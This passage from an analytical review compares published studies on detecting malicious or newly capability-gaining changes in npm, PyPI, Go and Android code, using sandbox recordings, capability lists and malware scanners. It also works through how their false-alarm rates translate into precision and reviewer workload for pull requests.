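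Ohm tested six packages, each with a malicious version and several clean ones. The results suggest that malicious and clean versions behave differently enough for the comparison to work. But he chose packages whose malicious code ran during installation, which is the easiest case.

The Package Analysis project does this kind of recording for whole registries. According to OpenSSF, it watches registries for new packages, runs each one in a sandbox, captures system calls and network traffic, and publishes the results in a public database. Brown (2022), in *The Package Analysis Project*, reports that simple searches of this database found about 200 malicious packages in just over a month. Most contained a short install script that sent a few details about the machine to an outside address. Brown thinks security researchers looking for rewards wrote most of the packages, since their behavior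 wasn't disguised. The addresses often helped identify the packages, because unrelated packages contacted the same few domains.

In *Scaling Up*, Handrick, Medeiros and colleagues (2025) tested the comparison of two versions on a much larger scale, running 4,076 pairs of Android apps. Each pair consisted of an original and a version that somebody had modified and republished. An automatic tool operated each app three times, for three minutes each time. The method classified the modified app as malware if it called any sensitive Android function that the original had not.

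On 102 pairs from an earlier study, this method had a recall of 90 percent and a precision of 91 percent. On the full set, precision was 84 percent, but recall fell to 40 percent. Most of the drop came from one family of advertising malware, gappusin, where the method missed 1,170 of 1,337 apps. The researchers examined 30 of these and found that 29 had changed the same function, apparently so that the app would download a different file. This change needed no new sensitive function, so the subtraction correctly found none. Without gappusin and one other family, recall was 72 percent.

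The method also did worse on small changes. It gave the right answer for 26.5 percent of pairs that were about 99 percent identical, compared with 77 percent of pairs that were 56 percent identical. Both figures exclude harmless apps that it correctly passed. This is discouraging for pull requests, which usually change a small part of a program, although gappusin probably accounts for much of this difference too.

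### Making more of the code run

Installing a package runs very little of its code. Zheng, Wei and colleagues (2024), in *Towards Robust Detection of Open Source Software Supply Chain Poisoning Attacks*, built OSCAR to run more of the code. It installs an npm or PyPI package, imports all its modules, and then tries to call every function and method they expose. This last step is a form of fuzzing, which means running code on generated inputs. OSCAR infers the likely type of each argument from the source code and chooses the values partly at random.

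OSCAR attaches logging code to selected library functions to capture their arguments before any encryption. A separate monitor records system-level activity in case an attacker has replaced a library function with a custom one.

Zheng and colleagues tested OSCAR on 500 malicious packages and 1,500 popular harmless ones from each of two registries, npm and PyPI. It found 459 of the malicious packages on npm and 423 on PyPI, and flagged only seven of the 3,000 harmless ones. It took two to three minutes per package. OSCAR applies fixed rules to one version at a time, so these results don't measure how well it would detect new behavior, but its method of reaching more code could also be used to compare two versions.

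Fuzzing can miss the exporter's upload. OSCAR's list of Python functions includes the one `HTTPSConnection` uses to send requests, so it could log both the report and the token. But it first has to call `export_report` with something that resembles a report. If it passes random text, the function fails at `report.date`, before the upload.

Zheng and colleagues list several reasons why OSCAR misses malware, including functions with complex arguments, malware that targets Windows when the sandbox runs Linux, and malware that behaves harmlessly when it detects a sandbox. They expect such cases to be rare because attackers want their code to run easily. This reasoning doesn't apply to ordinary application code, where a newly added upload might run only for a logged-in user with a full database and a particular setting, even if nobody tried to hide it.

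### Tracing a system call to a package

A recording of a whole application has the same weakness as a coarse static comparison: existing network access in one part hides new access in another. GoLeash addresses this for Go programs by working out which package made each system call. That is harder than it sounds, because Go's compiler combines an application and all its packages into a single program file. *GoLeash* describes these steps:

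1. Small programs inside the Linux kernel capture each system call together with the call stack, which is the chain of function calls that led to it. They use a Linux feature called eBPF, so the application needs no changes.
2. GoLeash translates the memory addresses in the stack into the names of functions and packages.
3. It starts at the most recent function, skips Go's standard library, and assigns the system call to the first application or third-party package it reaches.
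4. It looks up the capability in a table of 456 system calls. The table separates reading, writing, creating and deleting files, and also separates opening a connection from sending data.
5. In analysis mode, it adds the package, the capability and the chain of packages to a baseline. In enforcement mode, it checks them against that baseline.

The chain matters for changes like the exporter's call to `notify`. Suppose the exporter is written in Go, with `notify` in a package called `alerts`:

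```text
Baseline:  main → alerts → send data
New:       main → exporter → alerts → send data
```

GoLeash assigns both system calls to `alerts`, which already has permission to send data. It still flags the second because the baseline contains no route through the exporter.

Unlike Capslock, GoLeash can also examine what a second program does when the first one starts it. It can't attribute the second program's system calls to individual packages, so it uses one baseline for that entire program.

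The evaluation used five large Go applications: Kubernetes, etcd, CoreDNS, frp and geth. The researchers first recorded each application under a normal workload. They then inserted malicious code into every package that had run, one package at a time. The five kinds of malicious code included one that sent the system's configuration to a remote server and one that downloaded malicious files. These insertions produced 3,265 variants of the applications.

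GoLeash identified the injected behavior in 98 percent of cases, while monitoring each application as a whole identified it in 32 percent. These are averages over the five applications; counting every variant equally gives about 99 and 36 percent. Whole-application monitoring caught only two of the five behaviors, and largely by luck, because their code also accessed the process's resource limits, which some of the applications never did. It missed all 653 variants that sent out the system's configuration.

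GoLeash does well because most packages use few capabilities. The median package in Kubernetes used only three, so injected code nearly always needed another one. GoLeash missed malicious code only when the package already used every capability that code needed, such as reading files and sending data.

Hiding the malicious code had little effect on detection. The researchers hid it in a further 5,224 variants, using techniques such as reflection, plug-ins, C code and separate programs. Average detection stayed between 92 and 100 percent, although it fell to 77 percent for one behavior written in C and inserted into frp.

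GoLeash increased processor time per request by 1.3 to 5.1 percent, compared with 0.2 to 1.6 percent for the coarse monitor. It runs only on Linux, and it needs a table of function names that many production builds, including the standard Kubernetes build, leave out.

The 98 percent applies only to code that runs, because the researchers put the malicious code into functions they had already seen running and then repeated the workload. They saw no false alarms in the performance tests, but they point out that this was bound to happen because they used the same workload to build the baseline and to check it.

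### Reading the comparison with Capslock

*GoLeash* also reports a detection rate averaging 65 percentage points higher than Capslock's for unobfuscated code that sends out the system's configuration. This comparison covers only packages that ran during the workload. The paper calls the restriction conservative for GoLeash, but it excludes the packages that didn't run, where only Capslock can detect anything.

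A second analysis in the paper includes them. It counts an injection as detected if the malicious code needs a capability that the tool had not already assigned to the package. Adding up the results for the five applications gives:

| Packages analyzed by | Number | GoLeash detects | Capslock detects |
|---|---|---|---|
| Both tools | 288 | 284 | 176 |
| GoLeash only | 365 | 364 | 0 |
| Capslock only | 1,056 | 0 | 725 |
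| Total | 1,709 | 648 | 901 |

Capslock therefore detects more injections overall, but GoLeash is clearly better in packages that both tools analyzed, partly because its capabilities are more detailed. The second row also counts against Capslock in the 65-point comparison. The packages in that row ran but were missing from Capslock's call graph, typically because the program reached them through reflection or plug-ins, according to the paper. The group is surprisingly large, given that Capslock loads everything a program depends on, and a different setup might shrink it.

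The third row matters most for reviewing a change. More than half of the packages never ran, although the workloads were meant to exercise each application's main functions. GoLeash cannot detect a new capability in these packages until their code runs.

### When the tests never reach the new code

For a pull request, the obvious workload is the project's own test suite. The exporter's tests might check only the date format, or they might replace the network connection with a stand-in so that they run quickly and without internet access. Both are good testing practice, but in either case the recording would not show a connection to collector.example.

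An empty list of new behaviors can therefore mean either that the change added no capability or that the new code didn't run. A coverage tool, which lists the lines the tests executed, can help tell which. If the lines containing the upload never ran, the result for them is "unknown" rather than "nothing new". But if the tests used a stand-in for the real connection, the tool reports those lines as executed even though they never made one.

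The person who writes a change often writes its tests too, and so decides which parts of the change the tests run. With an honest programmer this only leaves gaps in coverage, but an attacker can leave the malicious path untested, or make it wait for a certain date or a machine that doesn't look like a sandbox.

*GoLeash* suggests fuzzing to run more of the code, and using Capslock to list capabilities that the source code could use but the workload didn't exercise. For a pull request, a reviewer could then focus on new capabilities that appear in the static scan but not in the test run.

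The sandbox also needs suitable settings. A made-up value for `REPORTS_TOKEN` would get the exporter past the line where it otherwise stops. If the sandbox also logs requests before encryption, it can search them for that value and detect the leak directly. Whether to allow internet access is a harder choice, because blocking it means that a program that downloads its malicious part shows only the attempted download, but allowing it could let the program do real harm.

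### Noise from the test run

A recording also contains behavior unrelated to the change. When npm installs a package, it copies files and contacts the registry. Test programs start processes and write temporary files and reports. These actions can end up in the list of new behaviors, as did the two addresses that belonged to Preflight's testing environment.

Some of this noise is easy to remove. Ohm found that installations give some files and folders random names, so the same file looks new each time. He removed the random parts before subtracting. OSCAR ignores requests to the local machine, changes in temporary folders and processes that npm starts. GoLeash leaves out system calls that Go itself makes without involving a package. Each exception also lets an attacker hide activity, and temporary folders are a common place to put a downloaded program.

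Behavior that varies between runs is harder to deal with. Suppose a program checks for updates in one run out of five, and a patch doesn't change this. If we run each version once, there is a 16 percent chance (0.8 × 0.2) that the check appears only in the new version and looks like a new network connection. Running each version three times and combining the results raises this to about 25 percent, because the check is more likely to appear in at least one run of the new version. Ten runs of the old version and one of the new reduce it to about 2 percent. Extra runs of the old version therefore reduce false alarms. Running the new version more often reveals more behavior, whether or not the patch introduced it.

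### Recording a capability or blocking it

The same recording can be used to inform a reviewer or to stop the program. *Wolf at the Door* (Wyss, Wittman and colleagues, 2022) describes Latch, a system for npm install scripts that can do either. Latch runs each script in a sandbox and summarizes its behavior in a manifest. Before an installation, it compares the manifest with the user's policy, which might forbid network connections or reading password files. For each rule, the user decides whether a violation produces a warning or stops the installation.

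The researchers tested two policies. A strict one for developers forbids network connections and writing to files. It caught all 102 malicious packages in their collection and would interrupt about one installation in 63. A looser one for registries caught 101 and would interrupt about one in 356, but the researchers had derived its rules from the same malicious packages.

A script can behave differently on the user's machine than it did in the sandbox, so Latch can also enforce a policy during installation, using the Linux security module AppArmor to block forbidden actions as they happen. AppArmor can't express all of Latch's rules, so the researchers gave it a stricter version of the developer policy. This version blocked every script that the manifest check had blocked, plus 6.2 percent of those that the check had allowed. In a sample of 50 of these additional blocks, more than half were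 mistakes caused by AppArmor's coarse handling of network connections. The average slowdown was less than 1 percent.

Latch stops protecting the user once installation ends. Ohm and colleagues cite research that more than 40 percent of supply-chain attacks start later, when the package runs. Their own system restricts packages at that stage, as does GoLeash, which can either log a violation or end the process. But GoLeash collects system calls from the kernel with a short delay, so the first forbidden call may already have gone through, and could have sent out a password, before the process ends.

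Blocking partly makes up for poor test coverage, because code that the tests missed is still checked when it runs. But it turns gaps in the baseline into failures. If the recorded workload never included the exporter's monthly archive job, a log entry takes somebody a few minutes to review, whereas ending the process stops the reports. *GoLeash* therefore recommends first trying a baseline in a staging environment or on a small part of the live system, and adding any legitimate behavior it missed. For code review, the baseline has to come from the version before the change. If the team records a new one after merging the patch, it will treat the upload to collector.example as normal behavior.

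## How often do harmless changes add a capability?

Suppose a user asks for the report exporter to save a copy of each report, and a colleague adds a line that writes the file. A scanner that flags file writing as a new capability is correct, but the flag is useless as a warning about an attack, and a more accurate scanner would still raise it. The number of such flags depends on how often ordinary changes add a capability. Published estimates for package updates range from about 0.5 percent to more than 60 percent.

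### Updates to 1,000 npm packages

The highest figures come from Ohm and colleagues, who built a system that blocks new capabilities in JavaScript packages. It uses syntax trees to list the built-in modules and global objects (those available without an import) in a trusted version of a package. After an update, a modified version of Node replaces any module or global object not on the list with a dummy that does nothing.

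To find out how often this would affect harmless updates, the researchers examined past updates of the 1,000 most depended-upon npm packages. They assumed that every version still on the registry was harmless. They grouped the updates by version number. A patch update should only fix bugs, a minor update adds features, and a major update may break programs that use the package.

| Type of update | Updates that use a new module or global object | Same, also counting individual operations |
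|---|---|---|
| Patch (1.0.1 to 1.0.2) | 14.7% | 20.4% |
| Minor (1.0.2 to 1.1.0) | 40.2% | 49.6% |
| Major (1.1.0 to 2.0.0) | 62.5% | 65.9% |

Many of these additions probably give the package no new access to the outside world. The list treats all modules and global objects alike, so `Buffer`, which handles raw bytes, counts as much as `child_process`, which starts programs. In 21.9 percent of minor updates, more than half of those that added anything, the only additions were global objects. But some global objects matter, such as `process`, which holds the environment variables, so we can't exclude all of these updates from the count.

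Ohm and colleagues tested the system on ten npm packages that had turned malicious in an update, and it stopped nine of the attacks. They couldn't trigger the malicious behavior of the tenth. Five of the nine programs crashed when the system intervened. Eight of the ten malicious updates were numbered as patches, the type of update in which harmless new capabilities are least common. That makes a new capability in a patch update more suspicious, although attackers can choose any version number.

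Counting individual operations stopped no additional attacks, because none of the packages had previously used the modules or objects that the attackers needed. But it raised the share of flagged patch updates by almost six percentage points.

Ohm and colleagues concluded that even for patch updates their system would probably cause too many false positives, meaning harmless updates that the system interferes with. Some flagged updates would still work, because an application may never run the code that needs the new capability. The 14.7 percent is therefore an upper limit on the share of patch updates that the system would break. A reviewer who only wants to know what is new would still have to look at every flagged update.

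### Why Google's figure is so much lower

Google runs Capslock on Go packages and publishes the results on deps.dev, its website about open-source packages. McClintock and Dethridge report in *Bringing Capslock analysis to deps.dev* that less than 2 percent of version updates introduce a new capability. That is less than a seventh of the lowest npm rate in the table.

The difference in language can't explain most of this gap, because another npm study found an even lower rate. *Containing Malicious Package Updates in npm with a Lightweight Permission System* (Ferreira, Jia and colleagues, 2021) uses only four permissions: network, filesystem, process and "all". "All" includes the other three and covers code that can run text as code or alter JavaScript's built-in objects. A package also needs every permission that its dependencies need.

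The researchers worked out the permissions for a year of updates to the 100 most depended-upon npm packages and all their dependencies. Only 27 of 5,042 updates, or 0.5 percent, needed more permissions than the version before. (The true share with something new may be slightly higher, since the paper groups other changes, such as a switch from filesystem to network, in a category that makes up 2 percent of updates.)

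Both npm studies examined heavily used packages and inferred capabilities from the source code, yet the lowest rate in the first is more than 25 times the rate in the second. The most likely reason is that their capability lists differ in length. Ferreira and colleagues' list has four entries, and Capslock's has 13. Ohm and colleagues count every built-in module and global object as a capability, and their finer list has 101 entries for the file module alone. Froh and colleagues' npm tool, which flagged 1.4 percent of versions, also used a short list.

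A low rate can also mean that packages already have most of the capabilities on the list. About a third of the 5,042 updates were to packages that held the "all" permission and so couldn't gain anything. Leaving them out raises the rate only to about 0.8 percent, so they don't explain much of the gap. The effect is stronger for whole applications. Capslock's *Know what your dependencies can do* shows sample output for a Go project whose 45 packages together have 11 of the 13 capabilities. A check of the whole project could report only two new ones, calls into C code and changes to the system's state.

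Counting calls made through dependencies could raise or lower the rate. A package can gain a capability because one of its dependencies did, even if its own code is unchanged. But it also starts with more capabilities, so it has fewer to gain. In Ferreira and colleagues' count of the whole npm registry, 21.9 percent of packages needed the "all" permission for their own code, and another 36.8 percent needed it only because of their dependencies. McClintock and Dethridge found that 9 percent of Go packages have a dependency that uses `os/exec`, the standard package for starting programs. If such a package later starts a program from its own code, a tool that counts both direct calls and calls through dependencies may report no new capability.

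The published data can't show how much each of these factors contributes:

- McClintock and Dethridge don't say how many updates they analyzed or how many were patch, minor or major updates. If nearly all were patch updates, the fair comparison is with 14.7 percent, but if many were major, the gap is larger.
- Ohm and colleagues don't make clear whether their update figures include changes in a package's dependencies.
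- The samples differ. Ohm and colleagues chose the most depended-upon packages, which may gain capabilities more or less often than the average Go package.

Nobody appears to have applied both a long and a short list of modules and objects to the same updates. The experiment would be fairly easy, because Ohm and colleagues published their code and the names of the packages they studied. Counting only modules and objects that give access to the network, processes, files or secrets would show how many of the flagged patch updates gained a capability that matters to a reviewer.

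### Choosing the categories

A longer list produces more flags, but not necessarily on the right changes. Take the exporter that already downloads exchange rates and reads its display language from the environment, now written in JavaScript with `https.get` and `process.env`. One programmer fixes the date format with `Intl`, a global object that formats dates for different countries. Another fixes it by editing the existing format text, but also reads a token from `process.env` and uploads each report to collector.example with `https.request`. Three lists, modeled on those in the two npm studies, would give these results:

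| Level of detail | New in the harmless fix | New in the fix with an upload |
|---|---|---|
| Four broad permissions | Nothing | Nothing |
| Modules and global objects | `Intl` | Nothing |
| Individual operations | `Intl.DateTimeFormat` | `https.request` |

The middle list does worst because it flags the harmless fix and misses the upload. The most fine-grained list also flags the harmless fix, but it catches the upload.

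A better list for this program would leave out `Intl` and divide network access more finely, for example by separating downloads from uploads or recording each destination. Ohm and colleagues similarly propose choosing or weighting the capabilities on their own list by how often malware uses them or how useful they would be to it. They point out that the file module is more useful to an attacker than the module that controls Node's JavaScript engine.

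The detail needed also depends on how much access the code already has. Capslock's website gives "A date formatter with network access?" as a warning sign. Four broad permissions would catch this in a small library that only formats dates. They were also enough for the three past attacks that Ferreira and colleagues replayed, because none of the attacked packages had needed any permission before.

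The exporter needs a more detailed list because it uses the network legitimately. The attacks that Ohm and colleagues tested provide little evidence about such programs, since the packages had never used the capabilities the attackers needed. The tests also excluded attacks that work only in a browser, such as the ten camouflaged ones that RogueOne missed. The finding that finer detail stopped no additional attacks may therefore not hold for code that already has a lot of access.

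Comparing smaller units of code also helps with this problem. *GoLeash*, for example, keeps a separate list of capabilities for each package. But with more lists, a harmless change is more likely to add a capability that one of them lacks.

The choice of list greatly affects a maintainer's workload. In Ferreira and colleagues' sample, each package or application faced an average of 66 updates a year. At their rate of 0.5 percent, a maintainer would see a new permission about once every three years. At 14.7 percent, the maintainer would see about ten flags a year, even if every update were a patch.

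Ferreira and colleagues acknowledge that phone users often ignore permission requests. They expect developers to pay more attention, partly because new permissions would be rare and developers can usually tell why a package needs one. This argument is convincing if there is one request every three years, but less so if there are ten a year, particularly if most of them concern objects like `Intl`. Each flag also takes more work to handle when the check blocks changes. The capcheck tool from git-pkgs can run as a GitHub Action that reports every new capability as an error, next to the first line of the project's own code on the call path. Someone then has to deal with the error even when the change was meant to add that capability.

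### Commits and pull requests

The figures so far are for published releases, which can each contain many separate changes. No published study appears to have measured how often a pull request adds a capability the code did not have before. The available data on pull requests and commits measure slightly different things.

In *Lessons from the Long Tail*, Wattanakriengkrai, Kula and colleagues (2023) collected pull requests from 1,500 npm libraries and kept the 63,829 that changed JavaScript files or the package's manifest. They searched the added lines for six features: new scripts, web requests, file access, low-level network connections, `eval` and `require`. The search flagged 12,465 pull requests, or about one in five. The rate varied little with popularity, from 21 percent for the libraries with the most dependents to 17 percent for those with the fewest.

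Most of these flags may not indicate a new capability. The most common matches were new scripts and `require`, which JavaScript programs use to load any module, including another file of the same project. The researchers also didn't check whether the library already had the feature, so moving an old line to another file could trigger a flag. But a text search of added lines also misses calls through existing helper functions, like the exporter's call to `notify`. The rate of new capabilities is probably well below one in five, but this study doesn't show how far below.

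Maintainers had merged about 71 percent of the flagged pull requests when the researchers collected the data. This suggests most were acceptable, though maintainers may have merged some without noticing the flagged feature.

Android apps allow a cleaner comparison because developers have to declare permissions in a manifest file, where a new permission appears as a new entry. *Who Added that Permission to My App?* (Krutz, Munaiah and colleagues) examined 331,318 commits to 1,402 open-source apps and found 4,494 added permissions. Since one commit can add several permissions, at most 1.4 percent of commits added any. Developers typically added permissions early in an app's life, so the rate for an established app is probably lower. In 106 cases, a developer later removed a permission that another developer had added.

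The 1.4 percent figure is the closest available for ordinary application code, but it covers only declared permissions. Once an app has permission to use the internet, a later commit can add an upload to a new server without changing the manifest. The share of commits that add new behavior could therefore be higher.

The rate is much higher over longer periods. In *Quantifying Permission-Creep in the Google Play Store*, Taylor and Martinovic (2016) compared snapshots of about 1.6 million apps, taken three months apart. They counted only permissions that protect sensitive data, such as a user's location or contacts. On average, 13.2 percent of the apps updated during a quarter gained at least one such permission, and 7.9 percent lost at least one. The permission to edit the user's calendar was both added and removed more often than any other, which Taylor and Martinovic think may reflect developers'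 confusion about when they need it.

The two Android results are compatible, because small chances add up over many commits. If an app receives ten commits in a quarter and each has a 1.4 percent chance of adding a permission, the chance of at least one addition is about 13 percent. This is close to Taylor and Martinovic's figure only by coincidence, since the studies covered different apps and permissions. But the calculation shows why we can't apply a rate for releases directly to pull requests.

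A smaller share of pull requests than of releases should be flagged, but a team that checks every pull request won't necessarily see fewer flags over a year than one that checks only releases. If all changes go through pull requests, every new capability in a release arrived in at least one of them.

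## How precise are the scanners, and does that hold for application code?

Nearly all published error rates for these scanners come from tests on packages, where a flag counts as correct only if the package is malicious. The rates therefore measure how well a scanner finds malware rather than capabilities, and applying them to a pull request for an application like the report exporter requires further assumptions.

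### Eleven tools on the same npm packages

In the largest npm comparison, Guo and colleagues ran 11 tools, some in several variants, on 6,420 malicious package versions and the latest versions of 7,288 popular packages that they presumed harmless. They kept each tool's default settings. The tools judged one version of a package at a time. (The tool that Froh and colleagues built to compare updates was not publicly available, so it is missing from the results.)

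These six results show the range:

| Tool | What triggers a flag | Recall | Harmless packages flagged | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Packj, reading the code | Any call to a listed function | 98.7% | 6,234 (85.5%) | 50.4% |
| Packj, running the code | Sensitive behavior in a sandbox | 95.5% | 4,656 (63.9%) | 56.8% |
| OSSGadget | Text patterns in any file | 91.6% | About 5,780 (79%) | 50.4% |
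| GuardDog, older version | Semgrep rules and package details | 89.9% | About 180 (2.5%) | 97.0% |
| IntelGuard | A language model's comparison with known malware | 93.8% | 108 (1.5%) | 98.2% |
| GENIE | Strict CodeQL queries | 46.1% | About 7 (0.1%) | 99.8% |

(The approximate counts follow from the published precision and recall.)

GuardDog and OSSGadget find almost the same share of the malware, but OSSGadget flags about 32 times as many harmless packages. OSSGadget's patterns match words wherever they occur, including in documentation. GuardDog had rules that matched only when data flowed from a sensitive source to the network, and it ignored a list of legitimate install commands.

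Guo and colleagues give most of the credit to the data-flow rules. That is hard to reconcile with how much GuardDog relied on its rules for install scripts and suspicious links. The list of exceptions probably matters more than they suggest, because without it the install-script rule would flag many ordinary packages. The results predate GuardDog 3.0, so they don't measure the current version's precision.

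The test set may slightly favor both tools. Three experts checked every malicious package, but they looked only at the code that GuardDog or OSSGadget had flagged, and they removed 1,367 packages in which they found nothing malicious. If both tools had flagged the wrong code in a malicious package, the experts could have removed the package by mistake, and the miss would not have counted against either tool.

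GENIE instead limits false alarms at the risk of missing attacks. One of its queries flags code only when at least three different pieces of system information reach the same web request. That combination is rare in harmless code, but the query misses attacks that steal only one secret, so it would miss the exporter patch with its single token.

Packj is the closest of these tools to a pure capability check. Its recall stayed above 97 percent for malware from every period, while the recall of SAP, a machine-learning tool, fell from 87 percent for malware from 2021 to 39 percent for malware from 2023. Malware had become simpler and looked more like ordinary code, but it still had to call sensitive functions. The weakness of checking for those calls is that most popular packages make them too.

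A capability match adds little to a flag from a better tool. Keeping only the GuardDog-flagged packages that Packj also flagged raised precision from 97.0 to 97.4 percent. Accepting a flag from either tool caught 665 more malicious versions than GuardDog alone, but also produced 6,015 more false positives.

### Which rules cause the false positives

*Cutting the Gordian Knot* (Guo, Liu and colleagues, 2026), by several of the same researchers, tested scanners on 2,363 malicious and 2,394 harmless Python packages from PyPI and broke down the errors by rule. As in the npm study, the harmless packages were popular ones.

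| Tool | False positives | Rules that most often caused them |
|---|---|---|
| GuardDog | 141 | Running text as code (58%) |
| Bandit4Mal | 1,927 | Web addresses (88%), reading files (56%), writing files (40%) |
| OSSGadget | 2,000 | Linux commands (97%), Windows utilities (87%), sending data out (72%) |
| PyPI's own former checks | 2,117 | Code that manipulates code during setup (97%) |

The percentages appear to be shares of each tool's false positives. They overlap because one package can match several rules.

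Many of these matches have nothing to do with a capability. The web addresses Bandit4Mal matched include links to project home pages and documentation, and PyPI's setup rule matched ordinary import statements. A scanner that parses the code properly could avoid such matches. But the file rules matched real file access, and GuardDog's most common error was flagging code that does run text as code, typically a setup script that runs `version.py` to get the version number. Better parsing can't remove those matches, because the code does what the scanner reports and the package is harmless.

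The number of flagged packages also understates the work of reviewing them. On a larger set of 18,137 packages, OSSGadget marked almost five million places in the code, about 273 per package, while GuardDog marked 11,420. PyPI's checks raised 31,242 alerts on a single file.

GuardDog's errors changed with the sample. On a set of newer packages, its recall fell from 94 to 68 percent, and suspicious links replaced code execution as the main source of false positives. Its false positive rate was 2.5 percent on npm and 5.9 percent on PyPI (141 of 2,394). The PyPI paper's text gives 4.3 percent, which doesn't match its own counts. A team should expect different rates on its own code from those in these studies.

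The researchers then used what they learned from these errors to build PyGuard, a tool that looks for sequences of actions instead of single calls and uses a language model to judge unclear cases. On the same test set, it produced two false positives and missed 19 malicious packages. In a three-month trial on new PyPI packages, it flagged 233, of which at least 219 were malicious. Context can evidently remove most of the false positives from capability rules, at least when the task is detecting malicious packages.

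Older figures look much worse. *A Benchmark Comparison of Python Malware Detection Approaches* (Vu, Newman and Meyers, 2022) found that three scanners flagged between 15 and 97 percent of harmless packages, depending on the tool and on which files it read. The study did not test GuardDog, so the range is a poor guide to current tools.

Vu and colleagues found that PyPI's rules for detecting when a setup script starts another program matched about as often in harmless packages as in malicious ones. Network use was more typical of the malicious packages. This suggests that a scanner should not give the two capabilities the same weight, though the result covers only setup scripts.

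### Working out precision for real traffic

About 47 percent of the packages in the npm comparison were malicious. Precision depends heavily on this share, and no real stream of packages or pull requests has one that high.

Let p be the share of changes that are malicious, r the recall and f the false positive rate. Out of N changes, pN are malicious and the scanner flags prN of them. The other (1 − p)N are harmless and it flags (1 − p)fN of those. Dividing the correct flags by all flags cancels N and leaves

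precision = pr / (pr + (1 − p)f).

Take a company with 10,000 pull requests a week, roughly the number that Lamb and colleagues report for Datadog. Assume that one of them is malicious and that the scanner has a recall of 95 percent. Both numbers are assumptions, since nobody has published a good estimate of either for pull requests. For f, we can try the 1.4 percent that Froh and colleagues measured on npm versions and the 0.03 percent that Datadog reports for its language-model reviewer:

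| False positive rate | False alarms per week | Precision |
|---|---|---|
| 1.4% | About 140 | 0.7% |
| 0.03% | About 3 | 24% |

With the higher rate, a reviewer would read about 147 alerts for each real attack. With the lower one it would be about four.

If ten pull requests a week were malicious instead of one, precision would rise to 6 and 76 percent, but the number of false alarms would hardly change, because nearly all the pull requests would still be harmless. A team that knows f for its own code can therefore predict its workload fairly well without knowing how often anyone attacks it, but it can't predict precision without knowing that too.

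For at least half the alerts to be real in the original example, the false-alarm rate f would have to be below about 0.0095 percent, or one false alarm in roughly 10,500 harmless pull requests.

Some data on p exist for package registries. Gao, Sun and colleagues (2025), in *MALGUARD*, scanned 64,348 new PyPI uploads over about five weeks and found 113 previously unreported malicious packages, or 0.18 percent. The true share must be higher, because the count excludes malicious packages that were already known or that the tool missed. Montaruli, Compagna and colleagues (2025), in *One Detector Fits All*, counted 216 malicious releases among about 91,800 on PyPI, or 0.24 percent.

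If 0.2 percent of packages were malicious, the npm results would look like this:

| Tool | Precision in the npm test | Precision at 0.2% malicious |
|---|---|---|
| OSSGadget | 50.4% | 0.2% |
| GuardDog, older version | 97.0% | 7% |
| IntelGuard | 98.2% | 11% |
| GENIE | 99.8% | 49% |

Differences of one or two percentage points in the test turn into large ones. The last figure is uncertain because it rests on only about seven false positives, so a few more or fewer would change it a lot. The figures are probably also too low for a whole registry, because popular packages set off more false alarms than ordinary ones. Even so, a scanner with 97 percent precision on a test set that is half malware can produce alerts that are nearly all false in daily use.

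Requiring two good tools to agree raises precision but lowers recall. When GuardDog and IntelGuard had to agree, precision was 99.5 percent in the test, which corresponds to about 30 percent at the lower prevalence. Recall was 86 percent, compared with 94 percent for IntelGuard alone.

### How many false alarms are too many?

Whether a scanner's false-alarm rate is acceptable depends on how many items a team has to check. PyPI's maintainers told Vu and colleagues that they could spend about 20 minutes a week on malware reports. They were already removing about 20 malicious packages a week, which took roughly a minute each. With 20,000 releases a week, even the lowest false-alarm rate that Vu and colleagues measured would produce about 3,000 false alarms. The maintainers considered a rate of 0.01 percent too high, and PyPI had by then switched off its own checks after two years.

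Montaruli and colleagues tested a machine-learning detector in two settings with very different volumes of releases. The detector scores each package using features such as the number of calls to sensitive functions and the amount of encoded text, and its user chooses the score at which it raises an alarm. For 37 days in 2025, the researchers collected every new PyPI release with source code and, separately, the 1,596 releases of the 584 Python packages that a large software company used.

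| False positive rate chosen on PyPI | Malicious PyPI releases found | False alarms per day, PyPI | False alarms per day, company |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10% | 196 of 216 | 247 | 1.2 |
| 1% | 180 of 216 | 21 | 0.05 |
| 0.1% | 92 of 216 | 2.2 | 0 |

The researchers recommend 0.1 percent for PyPI and 10 percent for the company. At 0.1 percent, PyPI's maintainers would miss more than half of the malicious releases but could keep up with the alarms. The company could handle the alarms from the more sensitive setting because it had so few releases to check.

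They think the PyPI setting fits into the 20 minutes, but they counted only the false alarms. At a minute each, the false and correct alarms together would take about 33 minutes a week. The overrun isn't large, but it matters to volunteers who want less of this work.

No attack hit the company's packages during the 37 days, so every alarm was false and the detector's precision was zero. It was still reasonable to run, because checking its alarms took a few minutes a day and it might have caught an attack. Precision matters less when alarms are rare and quick to check. The company could not use the 10 percent setting on 10,000 pull requests a week, because that would produce about 1,000 false alarms.

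Some scanners can't be tuned this way. Montaruli and colleagues also tested GuardDog on an older collection of Python packages and required a false positive rate of 1 percent. Its recall at that setting was only 6.6 percent, compared with 90 percent or more in the other two studies. The datasets differ, but recall was probably low because GuardDog's rules produced too few distinct levels of suspicion. By default it flags somewhat more than 1 percent of harmless packages, and a threshold strict enough to bring that below 1 percent also misses most of the malware. Vu and colleagues saw a similar effect when they required several alerts per package instead of one.

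### What changes with application code

Capability rules should be less precise as malware detectors on applications than on libraries, because applications normally use networks, files, other programs and configuration secrets, which many libraries never need. Guo and colleagues' npm results are consistent with this. Credential theft was among the hardest behaviors for the tools to detect because it uses the same functions as legitimate login code, which most business applications contain.

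The amount of code scanned also matters. In Vu and colleagues' test, PyPI's rules, applied to all Python files, flagged 94 percent of the popular Python packages, which averaged about 32,000 lines, and 68 percent of the random ones, which averaged about 2,800. A large application has even more places for a rule to match, but a pull request usually changes only a small part of it, and a scanner that reports only what is new ignores the rest. The false positive rate per pull request could therefore be higher or lower than the rate per package, and we can't tell which from package data.

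Even among packages, the flagging rate measured on one group doesn't hold for another. The setting that flagged 10 percent of harmless releases on PyPI flagged 2.9 percent of the company's packages.

### Measurements on ordinary repositories

Most measurements of ordinary repositories concern vulnerabilities, mistakes that an attacker could exploit. Help Net Security's *91% noise* reports that Ghost Security, a security vendor, scanned nearly 3,000 public GitHub projects in Go, Python and PHP for three kinds of vulnerability. One was command injection, where an outsider can alter a command that the program runs. More than 91 percent of the findings were false positives, and checking each finding by hand took about ten minutes on average.

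The figure is weak evidence of how precise a rule for process execution would be. Suppose the exporter runs a compression program on a file whose name is fixed in the code. A command-injection finding on that line is false, since no outsider can influence the command, but a finding that the exporter starts another program is true. Ghost Security's report also covers the time teams could save by having AI sort the findings, so a high share of false findings helps its argument.

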